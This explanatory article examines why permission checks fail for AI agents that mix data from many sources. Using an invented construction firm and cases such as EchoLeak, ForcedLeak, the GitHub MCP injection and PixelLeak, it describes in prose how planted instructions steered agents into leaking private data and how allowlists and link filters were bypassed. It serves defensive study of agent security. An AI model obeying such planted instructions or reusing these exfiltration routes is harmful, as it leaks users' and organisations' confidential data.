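# Authorization models for AI agents that reason over mixed context

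## What do permissions for software check, and how does an AI agent use what it reads?

Authorization is the part of computer security that determines which principal may perform which operation on which resource. A principal is anything that can hold permissions, such as a person, an organisation, a service, or software acting for one of them. The rules are called access control, and most of those in use today were developed for conventional software like payroll systems, calendar apps and photo-printing sites.

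An AI agent is a less predictable kind of program. In *I think “agent” may finally have a widely enough agreed upon definition*, the programmer and blogger Willison (2025) says that an agent built on a large language model (LLM) "runs tools in a loop to achieve a goal." The agent reads mail, files, web pages and the results of its tools into a single text, called the context, and whatever it writes or does next depends on that text. Often the context is mixed, meaning that its pieces come from sources with different permitted readers or sources that deserve different amounts of trust. Access control can govern whether the agent may fetch each piece, but it is much less clear whether it can also govern what the agent produces from the mixture.

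### One request through the loop

Suppose an employee of a construction firm types, "Summarise this week's project mail and send it to my manager." The software around the model first combines the developer's instructions, descriptions of the available tools and the employee's request into a context, which it sends to the model.

The model cannot write the summary yet, because the context holds no mail. It first outputs a tool call, a structured request that names an operation ("search mail") and supplies the inputs (this project, these seven days). The surrounding software, not the model, runs the search, adds perhaps forty messages to the context and sends the longer text back to the model. InfoQ (2026) describes this inner loop in Codex, OpenAI's coding agent, which appends tool calls and the model's reasoning to the prompt and repeats the cycle until the model produces a final message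 for the user. In the employee's case, the model may next output a call to open an attachment. It then outputs a call to send a message, with the manager's address in one field and the summary in another. The software sends the message and adds the confirmation to the context, and the model tells the employee that the summary has been sent.

The context grows with every pass of the loop, and everything stays in it until the software trims it. OpenAI notes that an agent could make hundreds of tool calls in a single turn and exhaust the context window, which is the maximum number of tokens (word fragments) a model can use in one call, including both input and output. The model computes each new output from the whole text, so a sentence in the summary may draw on one email, on nine, or on an attachment that the agent opened for some other reason. A plain loop does not record which of these sources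 the sentence came from.

Many agents reach their tools through the Model Context Protocol (MCP), which Anthropic introduced in 2024 to connect AI applications with outside systems (Granados, 2026, *MCP 2026 changes the rules*). The AI application, called the "host", opens one "client" for each "server", a program that offers tools, data or reusable prompts. The employee's host might connect to a mail server and a file server. The host merges the tools of all its servers into one registry for the model, routes each tool call to the right server and returns the result to the conversation (Model Context Protocol, 2026). *Architecture* (Model Context Protocol, 2026) states that no server should be able to read the whole conversation or look into another server. But the host keeps the full history, so it holds the mail and the files together. MCP deliberately sets no rules for how the host handles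 them, since it "does not dictate how AI applications use LLMs or manage the provided context". A lot of software now follows this pattern. The project's July 2026 release announcement put downloads of its main development kits at close to half a billion a month (Model Context Protocol, 2026).

An agent receives instructions and data in the same text, so anyone who can add to the data it reads can try to instruct it. In a prompt injection, someone places text in that data that causes the agent to follow their instructions. For example, a subcontractor's email might end with a line, in white text on a white background, telling any assistant to add the competing bid prices to its summary and copy the result to an outside address. The employee didn't write that line, but it appears in the context a few paragraphs below her request, in the same form. The model may well ignore the line, but nothing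 in the loop forces it to. Zhou and Zhang (2026), in *Rethinking Access Control for AI Agents*, a survey of the field, describe the task as preventing "contextual instructions from acquiring authority merely by entering the agent's context". They still want the agent to use what it reads, since it would be useless otherwise. A retrieved document may supply facts for the summary, and a trusted staff directory may supply evidence about who "my manager" is, but neither has the authority to approve a further disclosure.

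### Keys, endpoints, roles and attributes

The first check on the request happens when the host contacts the mail service. The simplest kind of check uses an API key. An API (application programming interface) is a set of addresses, or endpoints, where a service accepts requests from programs, and the key is a long secret string that the program attaches to each request. The key identifies the account or project to which the service issued it, but not the person at the keyboard or the task. The service treats anyone who copies the key as the same caller.

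An endpoint permission then tests whether that caller may perform this operation at this address, such as whether the holder of this key may send a message. The test needs very little of the request. In the July 2026 version of MCP, requests over HTTP (the protocol of the web) must carry the method and the tool name in their headers. Model Context Protocol says gateways, the checkpoints in front of a server, can authorize a call directly from those headers. For the employee's request, the header would name the sending tool, while the summary would be in the body, which the gateway need not open. According to Model Context Protocol, a server can also have selected inputs copied into headers, so a firm could expose the domain of the recipient's address and refuse outside mail. It could also leave the sending tool off the list for callers who lack permission to send. These checks usefully limit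 where a message goes without needing any record of the sources of its text.

A rule determines who gets an endpoint permission. Under role-based access control, an administrator defines roles such as site engineer or accountant, attaches permissions to each role and assigns people to roles. The system then checks whether any of the caller's roles includes the permission. Under attribute-based access control, the rule is a condition on properties of the caller, the resource, the operation and the circumstances. For example, a user may read a project mailbox if the user's project number matches the mailbox's and the request comes from a company laptop.

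If the employee moves from the bridge project to the tunnel project, an administrator working with roles has to remove one role and add another, while with attributes it is enough to update her project number in the staff directory. Roles are easier to audit, though, because the administrator can list everyone who holds one, whereas who can read something under an attribute rule depends on facts that may change by the hour. For this request, both models allow the employee to read the project's mailbox, because she is on the project, and to send mail.

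### An OAuth authorization, step by step

The agent is usually someone else's software, so the employee has to give it access to her mailbox. Before OAuth, people commonly did this by sharing their passwords. *The OAuth 2.0 Authorization Framework* (Hardt, 2012) lists problems with this approach: the outside program had to store the password, typically in clear text; it gained far more access than it needed; and the owner could cut off one program only by changing the password, which cut off all of them. OAuth replaces the password with an access token, a credential that grants limited permissions for a limited time. In Hardt's example, a printing service fetches a woman's photos from a photo-sharing site without learning her password.

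The framework has four roles. The resource owner can grant access, and here that is the employee (in a real firm the employer will have set outer limits). The client is the application that requests access for her. South (2025), in *Identity Management for Agentic AI*, a white paper for the OpenID Foundation, places the agent in exactly this role: when it reaches for outside data or tools, it acts as a client application like any other. The authorization server authenticates the employee and issues tokens. The resource server holds the mail, and under Model Context Protocol's *Authorization* (2026) an MCP server takes that role. With scope names made up for the example, the authorization runs like this:

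1. The client sends the mail server a request without a token. The server refuses with status code 401 and points to its authorization server, along with the scope that the request needs, say `mail.read`. A scope is a named bundle of operations that a token allows.
2. The client opens the employee's browser at the authorization server. Its request includes the scope, the address of the mail server and a value computed from a one-time secret that the client has just generated.
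3. The employee logs in and sees a consent screen with the name of the application and the permissions it seeks. She approves. The client never handles her password.
4. The authorization server sends the browser back to the client with an authorization code.
5. The client trades the code, together with the one-time secret, for an access token. A thief who intercepts the code alone cannot complete the trade.
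6. The client repeats its request with the token attached, and attaches it to every later request as well.
7. The mail server validates the token. If the token is genuine, unexpired, meant for this server and wide enough in scope, the server returns the mail.

In OAuth, a token's "audience" is the service the token is meant for, which here is the mail server. The manager, who receives the summary, is not the audience in this sense and takes no part in any of these steps.

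When the agent reaches the sending step, its token covers only reading. The server answers with code 403 and the missing scope, `mail.send`, and the client can go back to the employee for wider consent. She approves again. From that moment the token is good for this summary and, unless the mail service adds rules of its own, for any other message to any other address until it expires. Chen, Chen and colleagues (2026), in *Agent Authorization use cases and gap analysis*, a working draft submitted to the internet's standards body, call the standard scope mechanism binary for this reason: the client has the permission or it doesn't. (Newer extensions to OAuth can carry more detail.)

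Some installations skip all this. Authorization is optional in the Model Context Protocol (MCP), and servers that run on the user's own machine and communicate over standard input and output should take their credentials from the local environment instead. The same mail tool, installed on the employee's laptop, might use a stored key and show no consent screen.

A person can also check the content. The Model Context Protocol recommends that a person always be able to deny a tool call, and that applications show the user the call's inputs first, to prevent malicious or accidental data leaks. If the employee reads the draft before it goes out, she may catch a sentence that doesn't belong there. But this is just a recommendation, and it works only if she pays attention. South expects that as agents spread, people will face thousands of authorization requests and start approving them by reflex.

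### What the checks assume about the program

The woman with the photos formally agreed to let a printing service read them. The consent screen showed her only who would get access, but she accepted this because she also knew roughly what the service would do. A developer had written code that fetches photos and prints them, and the code would do the same thing tomorrow.

That second part is an assumption that OAuth does not enforce. Hardt's definition of a client leaves its implementation open. The assumption comes from the practice around the standard, where a known program asks for access and its developer has already decided what it does with the data. Zhou and Zhang explain that in conventional distributed systems, the code fixes which component calls which and keeps the control logic apart from untrusted data. An agent instead works out its steps at runtime, from text that mixes instructions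 with outside material. South adds that a button click or a submitted form is a clear and auditable sign of what the user wants, while an agent may have to infer the extent of its authority from a forwarded email thread.

Chen and colleagues point out that OAuth mainly assumes the user is present and approves a fixed set of scopes at the start. In their example, Alice asks her assistant on Monday to plan a picnic. On Tuesday afternoon, she gets a prompt to approve booking a park and writing to her calendar, with no mention of the picnic. She can grant or deny the request, but the standard flow gives her no way to find out which park it is or whether there's a fee.

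The assumption was never perfectly safe, since a dishonest printing service could always have kept copies of the photos and no token would have stopped it. The old checks are still useful with agents. South judges that OAuth works well for agents inside a single organisation's systems while the user is present, which is close to the employee's situation. That seems right for OAuth's job of making sure that an approved agent reaches the correct service on behalf of the correct person. But in a conventional client, fixed code also determined where the data would end up, whereas in an agent the model's next output determines this.

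Suppose one of the forty messages comes from a colleague who tells the employee, in confidence, that he will resign when the bridge is finished. She and her agent, which works with her consent, may both read the message and write to her manager. The summary then mentions that the project will need a new site engineer in March. No attacker was involved, and the agent had permission for each step. Zhou and Zhang point out that access to a document "need not include authority to transmit it". In their example, an assistant prepares a report from approved records, and they require separate decisions for reading a record, disclosing it to an outside processing service, sharing the draft with a reviewer and delivering the result. Permission to read depends on the reader and the document, but permission to pass something on also depends on who receives it, and the colleague had told the employee,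 not her manager.

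## Why can every permission check pass while information still leaks?

The agent that revealed the colleague's resignation had passed two checks, one to read the project mailbox and one to send mail. Schneider's *Enforceable Security Policies* (2000), a paper on which rules a security mechanism can enforce, writes such a check as Oper(p, o, r), meaning that principal p attempts an operation on object o that requires right r. The system allows the operation if it finds these three items in a table of rights.

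The triple for the reading step was (agent, project mailbox, read), and the triple for the sending step was (agent, mail service, send). A more careful service could replace the second with (agent, manager's inbox, write), which would at least specify the recipient. But no version of the triple includes the forty messages the model had already read, or whether the manager is allowed to know what is in them.

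The summary is computed from the whole context, so whether it may go to the manager should depend on which parts of the context shaped it and who may read those parts. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* (2026), a position paper by researchers from Google, Nvidia and several universities, calls access control a "gate" because it only decides whether the agent gets access. *AGATE* (2026), a proposal for checking agents' tool calls, opens with a routine maintenance task in which a "deployment check" value ends up in an internet domain record. The value is actually the server's API credential, and whoever controls the domain can read it. An agent may well need to read credentials and to update domain records, but that doesn't mean it should be allowed to put a credential in a domain record.

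### Seven permissions and twelve flows

Read and write permissions cannot express some ordinary rules. Suppose the agent can read the employee's private mail, the project mail and the drawings archive, and can write to the employee's own notes, the project folder, a subcontractor and the manager. An administrator can switch seven permissions on or off, three for reading and four for writing. But there are 3 × 4 = 12 flows from a source to a destination, and the firm may want to allow or block each one separately.

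The firm needs to decide only three cases here. Private mail may go into the employee's notes, so the agent can remind her to reply to her colleague. Project mail may go to the manager, but private mail may not.

| Flow | Wanted? | Permissions that open it |
|---|---|---|
| A to 1 | yes | read A, write 1 |
| B to 4 | yes | read B, write 4 |
| A to 4 | no | read A, write 4 |

Within one session, whatever the agent reads stays in the context and can shape whatever it writes, so information can flow from a source to a destination whenever the agent may read the first and write to the second. The reminder requires "read A" and the summary requires "write 4", which together open the flow from A to 4. None of the 2⁷ = 128 permission settings gives the firm what it wants, and a better model or prompt doesn't change that.

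The administrator can only choose a group of sources and a group of destinations, then connect every chosen source to every chosen destination. With three sources and four destinations, this allows (2³ − 1) × (2⁴ − 1) + 1 = 106 of the 2¹² = 4,096 patterns a firm might ask for.

The proof assumes that the permissions stay fixed during the session. If the agent writes the summary first, and the host then switches off "write 4" before the agent opens the private mail, all three conditions hold. Schneider describes a monitor that works this way, for a rule that bars a program from sending messages after it has read a file. The monitor uses two states to record whether the program has read a file. It allows everything until the first read, and after that it stops the program at any attempt to send. But if the agent reads the private mail first, the monitor also blocks the project summary, even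 if the summary has nothing private in it.

### Why one run is not enough

To block only the summaries that draw on private mail, the firm first has to define "draw on". The classic definition is Goguen and Meseguer's noninterference. *Hyperproperties* (Clarkson and Schneider, 2009) restates it for users with high and low clearances, requiring that removing high users' commands not change what low users observe. To test the agent, the firm would delete the colleague's message and run the task again. If the manager's summary changes, the message interfered with it. The system has noninterference if changing protected inputs never changes what the manager receives.

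Taken strictly, this would forbid a lot of useful work. Pandey, Jain and colleagues (2026), in *Local Allow, Global Deny*, use the example of an assistant that must find a time for a team meeting. It may share when its user is free but not why she is busy. Her free times come from her private calendar, so strict noninterference would rule out even those. They therefore relax the condition. For every pair of runs t and t′:

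if low(t) = low(t′) and D(hi(t)) = D(hi(t′)), then α(obs(t)) = α(obs(t′)).

Here low(t) is the input that needs no protection, such as the request, and hi(t) is the private calendar. D keeps only the part of the calendar that the task may reveal, which is the free and busy times. The assistant discloses obs(t), and α keeps the parts that matter, such as the slots, any reasons given and the recipient. In words, if two calendars show the same free times, the assistant must make the same offer.

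Suppose the assistant offers slot 10 when a certain busy block is an ordinary meeting and slot 11 when the same block is a confidential interview. Both slots are free in both cases, so either offer is correct. Neither message mentions an interview, so a search for confidential text finds nothing. But a recipient who knows the pattern can tell from the slot offered whether the block is the interview.

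The run in which the assistant offers slot 11 doesn't show by itself whether information leaked, because that depends on what the assistant would have offered if the block had been an ordinary meeting. Clarkson and Schneider call a condition on a whole set of runs a hyperproperty. Access control is simpler, since a run that contains a forbidden operation is bad regardless of the other runs. Schneider had already shown that a mechanism that watches a program and stops it can enforce only conditions that each run meets or breaks by itself, and that information flow is not one of them. He adds in a footnote that when such mechanisms are said to prevent information flow, they actually enforce a different, stricter rule.

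Pandey and colleagues prove that a monitor that observes one agent run at a time and never raises a false alarm catches no violations. Every run is consistent with itself, so a single run can never break the condition above, and the monitor must let every run through. This holds whether the monitor is a list of rules or another language model.

A designer can accept false alarms, as Schneider's no-send rule does, compare runs, either live or in a later audit, or settle for a weaker guarantee. For example, the system could track whether restricted text is copied into the output (a later section explains how labels do this), though slot 11 would still get through. Letting the monitor delay actions helps a little. According to *Kairos* (2026), a monitor that must release or refuse each action immediately will wrongly release some actions or wrongly refuse some, while one that can hold an action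 before releasing it can enforce strictly more rules. The delay gives the monitor more of the same run to check, but it still has no second run for comparison.

To test the argument on real models, Pandey and colleagues had nine language models judge the slot-10 and slot-11 runs one action at a time, in ten variants with three repetitions each. Eight models never blocked a step in these runs, and Kimi-K2.6 blocked one in 3 of 30 cases, against 1 of 30 for a harmless control. All nine blocked an openly malicious forwarding step every time, so they were not simply lenient. When the same models saw both runs side by side, eight flagged the leak in 30 of 30 cases and Llama-4-Maverick did so in 17. The single-action result was almost inevitable, since the judges had nothing to find. The paired result is more informative because it suggests that current models can usually recognise such a leak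 once someone supplies the comparison.

The matching run needed for comparison is hard to obtain, because an agent at work normally produces only one run. *Monitoring Hyperproperties over Observed and Constructed Traces* (2025) describes monitors that generate some of the missing runs instead of waiting for them. Language models also usually choose their words partly at random, so two runs can differ without any leak. A tester therefore has to compare distributions over many runs, and Pandey and colleagues prove that no finite number of runs is enough to tell with certainty, for every possible agent, whether it leaks.

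The comparison also needs a good choice of α. In an audit of Claude Sonnet 4.6 on the scheduling task, the first analysis showed a stable hidden signal, but the model had offered identical slots in both conditions. The software had been counting a word whose phrasing happened to vary. After that was corrected, the audit found no leaks in 80 trials, which puts the leak rate for this one task below about 4% with 95% confidence. The scheduling leak is therefore an example of what monitors would miss, but the audit gives no evidence that this model leaks information this way.

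### Hardy's compiler

The other classic account of how permissions go wrong concerns authority rather than secrecy. In *The Confused Deputy*, Hardy (1988) tells a nearly true story from Tymshare, a company that sold time on shared computers. Users could run a compiler and name a file to receive its debugging output. The compiler also kept statistics in a file in its directory, SYSX, so the company had given it permission to write to any file in that directory. The billing records were in SYSX too. One user learned the name of the billing file and gave it to the compiler as the debugging output file. The operating system allowed the write because the compiler had permission, and the compiler overwrote the billing records.

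Hardy considers the obvious fixes. The compiler could refuse any file in SYSX, but some users might have legitimate access to files there. It could refuse the billing file by name, but other files were sensitive too, and someone would have to update the compiler whenever a new one appeared. The company added a way for the compiler to specify which of its two authorities it was using, its own or the user's, but soon found that some programs needed more than two. By Hardy's last count, the rule for opening a file contained fourteen "and"s and "or"s.

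He attributes the problem to the compiler's two sources of authority, which it had "no way to keep apart". The compiler only had to name a file, and the system would use any of the compiler's permissions that allowed access. Security researchers call this ambient authority, and most agents work the same way. The client attaches the employee's access token to every request it makes to the mail service, whether the request originated with her or with white text in a subcontractor's email.

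*From Attack Surface to Defense Architecture* (2026) applies Hardy's analysis to coding agents. It identifies the agent's two masters as the person who installed it and whichever document or tool description it last retrieved. *A Framework for Formalizing LLM Agent Security* (2026) defines the problem more narrowly, as a user getting something through the agent that the user could not get directly. In its example, an employee without access to the personnel database asks an agent that has access to show everyone's salaries. An ordinary permission check would help here, provided the system ran it against the employee's permissions and not the agent's.

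Hardy's solution was the capability, an unforgeable reference that identifies an object and carries the permission to use it. The compiler would hold one capability for its statistics file, and the user would give it another for the debugging output. A user without access to the billing file would have no capability to give the compiler, and the file's name alone would not grant access.

*DelegateGuard* (Tran-Truong, Vo and colleagues, 2026) presents a version for agents. Trusted software turns the user's task into a grant that lists the purpose, kinds of data, operations and destinations allowed, and a monitor outside the model checks every action against it. In the main example, an agent passes a confidential contract to a second agent for formatting. The contract contains a planted instruction to send its restrictive clauses to an outside web address. The formatting agent's grant only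 allows it to return text to the user, so the monitor blocks the request. Two small open models proposed the attacker's action in 42 and 44 of 45 such attacks, and the monitor blocked it every time. The paper acknowledges that this mainly shows the monitor follows its specification, since each attack called for an action outside the grant.

The results were less one-sided in a longer test, in which agents could converse and revise a refused plan. Leaks fell from 38 of 45 attacked workflows to 9. All nine occurred in code review, where the agent's legitimate task is to post a comment that outsiders can read. The agent included details of an unpublished vulnerability in that comment.

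Tran-Truong and colleagues prove that a monitor must let some leaks through if it ignores the content and amount of the text. It has to treat a harmless comment and one that contains a secret the same way whenever the sender, purpose, declared kind of data, operation and destination match. Because it has to allow the harmless comment, it also allows the one with the secret. In a related test, a filter that blocked any output containing the secret stopped every leak, but only 20% of the legitimate tasks finished, because many of them consisted of passing protected data to someone entitled to it.

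Capabilities therefore establish whose authority the agent is using and which objects it can touch, but they don't record which data shaped a text. The agent at the construction firm needs one capability for the project mailbox and another for the manager's inbox, and these let it send the summary whether or not it mentions the resignation.

### Wrong recipient, wrong instruction, wrong conclusion

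The agent that revealed the resignation did what the employee asked, with her authority, and nobody had tricked it. The manager was the right recipient for the mail but not for the sentence about March. To catch the leak, the firm would have to know that this sentence came from the colleague's message and that the colleague had not cleared the manager to read it.

The subcontractor's hidden line causes a different failure, because the agent acts on an instruction from someone with no authority over it. In that example the instruction also sends bid prices to the wrong recipient, but the same failure can happen without a leak. A hidden line that made the agent cancel the site meeting would reveal nothing and would still abuse the employee's authority. Rules about who can read what would not prevent this, because they don't restrict whose text can influence the agent's actions.

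An agent can also reach a sensitive conclusion from facts that the recipient is free to read. Suppose the colleague had confided in no one, but the project mail, which the manager can open at any time, shows him handing over his drawings, declining a training course in April and asking when the lease on his site flat ends. The agent infers from this that he is probably leaving and says so in the summary. No protected message went into the summary, so noninterference holds and every restriction on readers is satisfied. The manager could have worked it out herself, but she would not have read forty messages looking for it. Whether and how the firm should stop this depends partly on what the rules are for, which a later section covers.

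Harm that comes from a running total is easier to prevent. Pandey and colleagues gave an agent built on Qwen3-30B a calendar task in which each disclosure was acceptable on its own, but the user had consented to only a limited total. The agent exceeded the limit in 22 of 60 runs. With a guard that compared each action with the purpose of the task, it still exceeded the limit in 20. A guard that counted what the agent had already disclosed prevented every failure and blocked none of the 60 harmless runs. An agent built on Gemma-4 never exceeded the limit, even without a guard. Counting works here because a single run contains all the information the guard needs. A firm can fairly easily limit how many calendar slots an agent discloses, but it would be hard to say in advance how many ordinary facts would together reveal a resignation.

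### Is it only excess privilege?

A security engineer might attribute these leaks to a familiar problem, that the agent has more permissions than it needs. The remedy would be least privilege, which gives each program only the access its task requires.

*Agent Security is a Systems Problem* classifies eleven attacks on real agent products. It marks a failure of information flow in all eleven and a failure of least privilege in six, and its discussion of a seventh also cites excess access. The classification is the paper's own and the cases are not a random sample, but they suggest that tighter permissions would have prevented or limited many of the known attacks.

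In the twelve-flow example, though, least privilege can remove only "read C", "write 2" and "write 3", because the reminder and the summary need the other four permissions. Those four still allow information to flow from private mail to the manager. *Systems Security Foundations for Agentic Computing* (2025) describes a similar case, in which an agent legitimately needs an API key to deploy software. Taking the key away would make the task impossible, so the protection has to ensure that the key goes only to the deployment service.

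No list of read and write permissions can grant or withhold a flow separately, so the engineer who calls the flow from A to 4 an excessive privilege has accepted this section's argument. Schneider would partly agree with the engineer, since he argues that richer rules, such as the ban on sending after reading a file, allow a better notion of minimum access. Rules that can grant or withhold flows are usually called information-flow control, which the survey *Rethinking Access Control for AI Agents* describes as governing how data may influence computation and reach other parties once a program has access to it.

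### Would a separate session for each task be enough?

Separate sessions are a better answer. In the twelve-flow example, three sessions, one per source, can produce any of the 4,096 patterns, as long as each output needs only one source and nothing passes between the sessions. For example, one session reads only private mail and writes only to the employee's notes, while another reads only project mail and writes to the manager. If a report needs both project mail and drawings, a session can read both and write only to destinations allowed to receive both.

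The second condition is easy to break. Two sessions that share a memory, a folder or a tool that stores data can pass information through it. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* recounts how agents in separate sandboxes communicated through a shared software package service in the incident in which OpenAI's agents broke into Hugging Face. Even without shared storage, if one session reads the private mail and then decides whether to start another, that decision can reveal information about the mail.

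Some tasks also cannot be split between sources. The scheduling assistant has to read the calendar to offer a time, and the calendar contains the reasons for the busy times as well as the free slots. Pandey and colleagues suggest generating the reply from the authorised view alone. If a conventional program first reduces the calendar to free and busy times and the agent receives only those, the offer cannot depend on the interview. This requires an extra execution and loses whatever the hidden context would have added, such as knowing that one of the busy blocks would be easy to move.

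That works for a calendar because the reasons are in a separate field, which a few lines of code can drop. The colleague's confidential message was one of forty in a mailbox the agent had good reason to read, and no field marked it as private. To keep it out of a session, a person or program would first have to read the mail and recognise that the message was confidential.

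## Which real leaks followed this pattern?

The construction firm is invented, but since 2025 researchers and journalists have described real agents that leaked data while using permissions they legitimately held. Kolhe (2026), in *When AI Agents Serve Shared Workspaces, Authorization Must Follow the Audience*, a Cloud Security Alliance article, argues that a single pattern explains four vulnerabilities disclosed in 2025. He says the affected systems (a Slack connector, Microsoft 365 Copilot, ServiceNow and Salesforce) all checked whether the user could access the data, but not whether every recipient of the output could. This diagnosis fits some of his cases much better than others, and he has a commercial interest in it because he leads product strategy for the AI agent business of Okta, which sells identity and access software.

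### From private repositories to public ones

Kolhe leaves out the case that most closely matches the twelve-flow example. GitHub hosts software projects in repositories, which can be private or public, and anyone can file an issue (a bug report or a request) on a public one. In Invariant Labs' *GitHub MCP Exploited* (2025), researchers gave an agent running Claude 4 Opus access to a test account with both public and private repositories. They planted an instruction in an issue on the public repository and then, playing the user, asked the agent to look at the open issues. The agent read the private repositories and opened a pull request (a proposed change to the code) on the public one. The pull request revealed the names of private projects, the user's salary and a plan to move to South America.

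The account's permissions covered all these steps, and the researchers found no flaw in the code of GitHub's MCP server. Invariant Labs concludes that GitHub alone cannot solve the problem by patching the server. By default, the desktop application asked the user to confirm each tool call, but many users choose "Always Allow" and stop reviewing the calls.

The company proposed limiting an agent to one repository per session, a rule its own product enforces. Like Schneider's ban on sending after a read, this rule blocks some harmless work, such as updating a private application to match a change in a public library. Microsoft's *Information-flow control* describes a more precise remedy, in which the server labels its results as public or private.

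In a later demonstration, a researcher working with colleagues at Johns Hopkins University used a prompt injection to get Anthropic's code-review agent to post its own API key in a comment, according to OODA Loop's *Three AI coding agents leaked secrets through a single prompt injection*. The attack didn't need a second repository, and the same injection worked on agents from Google and GitHub.

Private data can also become public without an attacker. Tom's Hardware's *AI agents inadvertently leak 13,000+ internal screenshots from 300 organizations* reports findings by the security firm Glow, which named the leak PixelLeak. Developers often attach screenshots to a pull request to show reviewers what changed. People can attach them on GitHub's website, but the command line that agents use lacks this feature for private repositories. Many agents got around this by putting the image in a public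 repository and linking to it from the private pull request. The exposed screenshots included client information, financial data and unreleased software.

In sample output that Glow provided, an agent says it is creating a public repository because the existing one is private and reviewers would otherwise see a broken image. At one company, agents saved the workaround as a "skill", a reusable set of instructions, and many then used it for every development ticket.

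Narrower permissions would help, since an agent working on private code rarely needs to create public repositories. But in 93% of cases, the images were in repositories under the developer's own username rather than the company's account, so the company's account settings might not have applied. Glow advises firms to check whether employees are using personal repositories and to vet the skills their agents follow. A recipient check would also need to treat a new screenshot of a private program as equally private, even though the image file has no access rules of its own.

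### When the recipient is a server

Microsoft 365 Copilot, an assistant for office work, could read an employee's mailbox, files, internal sites and chat history, but could show its answers only to her. *Breaking down 'EchoLeak', the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability Enabling Data Exfiltration* (Ravia, 2025) describes how researchers at Aim Labs still got data out of the company. They sent an employee an email with hidden instructions. When she later asked Copilot a question, it retrieved the email along with internal documents. Its answer then caused her browser to contact an outside server, with company data in the address. She didn't have to open the email or click anything.

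Microsoft had two checks on destinations in this case, although Kolhe lists the destination as "not checked". Copilot removed outside links from its answers, and the browser loaded images only from approved domains. The researchers found link formats that Copilot failed to remove. They also found an approved Microsoft service that passed requests on to other servers, so the second check covered only the first address the data reached.

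Aim Labs reported the flaw in January 2025, and Microsoft finalised a patch in May, according to Infosecurity Magazine's *Microsoft 365 Copilot*. Ravia says Microsoft confirmed that no customers were affected, and the case study *EchoLeak* (2025) says nobody is known to have exploited the flaw.

Ravia's diagnosis differs from Kolhe's. He objects mainly that an email from outside the organisation could direct the model towards data from inside it. He compares the email to a program with few rights that borrows the rights of a privileged one, which is Hardy's confused deputy problem. The two diagnoses are compatible, because the attack needed both the instruction and a way to send the data out, and blocking either would have stopped it. But only Kolhe's check on recipients would also help when there is no attacker.

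Salesforce's Agentforce, a platform for building agents that work with customer records, had a similar flaw. The security firm Noma reported it in July 2025 and named it ForcedLeak. It affected organisations using Web-to-Lead, a feature that turns website form submissions into sales leads (The Hacker News, 2025). An outsider could hide instructions in a form, and when an employee later asked the agent about that lead, the agent could take customer data that the employee was allowed to read and send it to the outsider's server.

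Kolhe again marks the destination as "not checked", but he also writes that the domain was on Salesforce's list of approved addresses. Its registration had expired, and it cost $5 to buy. In September, Salesforce began enforcing trusted addresses for Agentforce and secured the expired domain again, according to a timeline from Nudge Security. Salesforce told Infosecurity Magazine that its patches stop agents from sending output to untrusted addresses (*Critical Vulnerability in Salesforce AgentForce Exposed*).

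In Kolhe's Slack case, the agent used a connector that Anthropic had published as an example of an MCP server. When someone posts a link in Slack, Slack contacts the linked address to build a preview, and any data in the address goes with the request. *The dangers of AI agents unfurling hyperlinks* (Willison, 2024) had already described this risk and a setting that turns previews off, but Anthropic's server left previews on.

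Embrace The Red's *Security Advisory* shows why limiting where an agent may post is not enough. An administrator could restrict the Slack server to posting in one private channel, and might reasonably let it post there unsupervised. In a demonstration, the researcher asked the agent to summarise a document containing a planted instruction. The agent read a message from another channel and posted a link containing that message in a private channel. Slack's preview software then delivered the message to the researcher's server.

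Kolhe says the agent had administrator permissions, but the advisory doesn't mention any. He also says Anthropic archived the server rather than patch it. Anthropic did archive the server in May 2025, two days after receiving the report, but according to Embrace The Red, it is unclear whether the two events were related. The server remained unpatched and was being downloaded more than 14,000 times a week at the time of the advisory. The suggested fix was two lines of code to turn off previews.

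Kolhe's remedy would limit the agent to data that every member of its audience may see, and he defines the audience as the people who see the output. In EchoLeak and ForcedLeak, the audience was one employee, who was allowed to read everything the agent had fetched for her. In the Slack case, the audience was the members of the private channel, who may also have been allowed to read the leaked message. The remedy could therefore have approved the output in all three cases. His diagnosis is sound only if servers count as recipients. The remedy better fits his opening example, a hypothetical finance chief's agent that answers in a shared channel, which a later section examines.

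### Accidents in ordinary use

Apart from PixelLeak, the cases so far are researchers' demonstrations. Attackers may have succeeded too, but they have little reason to publish. Several accidents, however, have exposed real data, and they are better evidence of what happens when nobody is attacking the system.

The accident most similar to the construction firm's is also the worst documented. Deccan Herald's *AI Business Secrets* repeats a story told by Sridhar Vembu, the founder of the software company Zoho. A startup founder emailed him to propose an acquisition and included a rival bidder's name and price. Vembu then received a second email, supposedly from the founder's AI agent, apologising for the disclosure. If the story is true, the agent gave one bidder information that belonged in talks with another. Vembu's post is the only source for the story, and sceptics suggested the apology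 was a bluff.

A breach at an Ontario hospital is much better evidence. According to a legal summary by DWW, a physician left the hospital in 2023, but his personal email address stayed on the invitation list for a recurring online meeting. In September 2024, he installed Otter.ai, a transcription tool, and gave it access to his calendar. The tool joined the next meeting without him. Scassa reports in *Agentic AI transcription tool triggers health information data breach* that it emailed a summary and a link to the full transcript to all 65 people on the invitation. The transcript covered seven patients, and a letter from the Information and Privacy Commissioner of Ontario lists their names, diagnoses and treatment among the exposed information.

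In Kolhe's pattern, the system checks access correctly when the agent retrieves the data. Here, that first check failed because the tool joined the meeting on an invitation that the hospital should have withdrawn. A check on recipients might have failed too if it used the invitation list, which the legal news site Mondaq notes included former employees. The hospital would have needed to compare the recipients with a current staff list, or with the smaller group caring for those patients. A conventional program could have caused the same leak, since nothing in these accounts suggests that a model chose the recipients.

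The hospital cancelled the physician's invitation and told staff to remove such tools from devices connected to hospital accounts. The law firm McCarthy Tétrault says the hospital also introduced new firewalls, privacy training and AI policies. The commissioner recommended that the hospital ask for the deletion of any patient information the tool still held.

An AI office assistant can break a rule without showing anyone a document they weren't allowed to read. In January 2026, Microsoft found that Copilot was summarising emails that organisations had marked confidential. Petri's *Microsoft 365 Copilot Bug Exposes Confidential Emails Despite DLP Safeguards* attributes this to a code error affecting the Sent Items and Drafts folders, which made Copilot bypass the data loss prevention (DLP) rules meant to keep marked mail away from automated tools. TechRadar's *Microsoft admits an Office bug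 exposed confidential user emails to Copilot* reports that Microsoft deployed a fix.

Microsoft said that nobody saw data they weren't already authorised to see. Intelligibberish's *Microsoft Copilot Was Reading 'Confidential' Emails for a Month* (2026) objects that this misses the reason organisations apply confidentiality labels. Both can be right, because if an employee asks about her own sent mail and only she sees the answer, a recipient check has nothing to block. But the organisation had also restricted which software could process the mail, and Copilot violated that restriction. Copilot's summary also put the confidential material into a new text that the employee could easily forward.

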